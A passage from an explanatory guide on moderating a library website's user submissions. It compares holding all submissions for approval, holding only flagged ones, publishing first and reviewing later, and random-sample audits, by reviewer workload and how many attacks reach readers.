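The library can detect this by also reading a random sample of the submissions that the filter didn't flag. If it read 50 a month, it would have about a 5% chance of finding the single attack in the table. If 18 attacks were getting through, the chance of finding at least one would be about 60% in the first month and about 85% over two months. This sample is too small to keep attacks off the site, but it can show that the filter has stopped working.

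### Before publication, afterwards, or a sample

Instead of holding submissions for approval (pre-moderation), a site can publish at once and review later, or review only some of the submissions. For the library's 1,000 submissions, with reviewers who make no mistakes, the arrangements compare as follows:

| Arrangement | Items to read | Attacks published | Who waits |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hold everything | 1,000 | 0 | Every visitor |
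| Hold flagged items only | 39 | 1 | About 20 honest visitors |
| Publish everything, then review all of it | 1,000 | 20, until a reviewer reaches them | Nobody |
| Publish everything, then review a random 50 | 50 | 20, of which the sample finds about 1 | Nobody |

Reviewing submissions after publication takes as much work as holding every submission for approval, and readers see the attacks in the meantime. It suits a busy discussion, where a delay of several hours would end the conversation and other participants will report what they notice. It is a poor choice for a page that search engines and other language models copy. Attacks also stay online until someone reviews them. If the library's staff reviewed at the speed of Wikipedia's volunteers, about 18 of the 20 attacks would still be online after a month.

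Holding only flagged items takes the least work of the arrangements that keep most attacks off the site, but reviewers never see what the filter misses. The library could accept that for questions that only staff will read. Holding everything is safer for answers published under the library's name, because a wrong telephone number could cost a reader money. The library can reduce the work by choosing only the 20 most useful of each month's 1,000 questions to publish, much as AISafety.info's editors choose what to answer.

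When reviewers fall behind, pre-moderation delays honest visitors' text but keeps unread text off the site, whereas publishing first leaves unread text public until someone reviews it. Operators who don't know who will read the queue during a holiday, or when submissions suddenly double, should therefore hold everything by default and close the form when the queue grows too large for their reviewers to clear.
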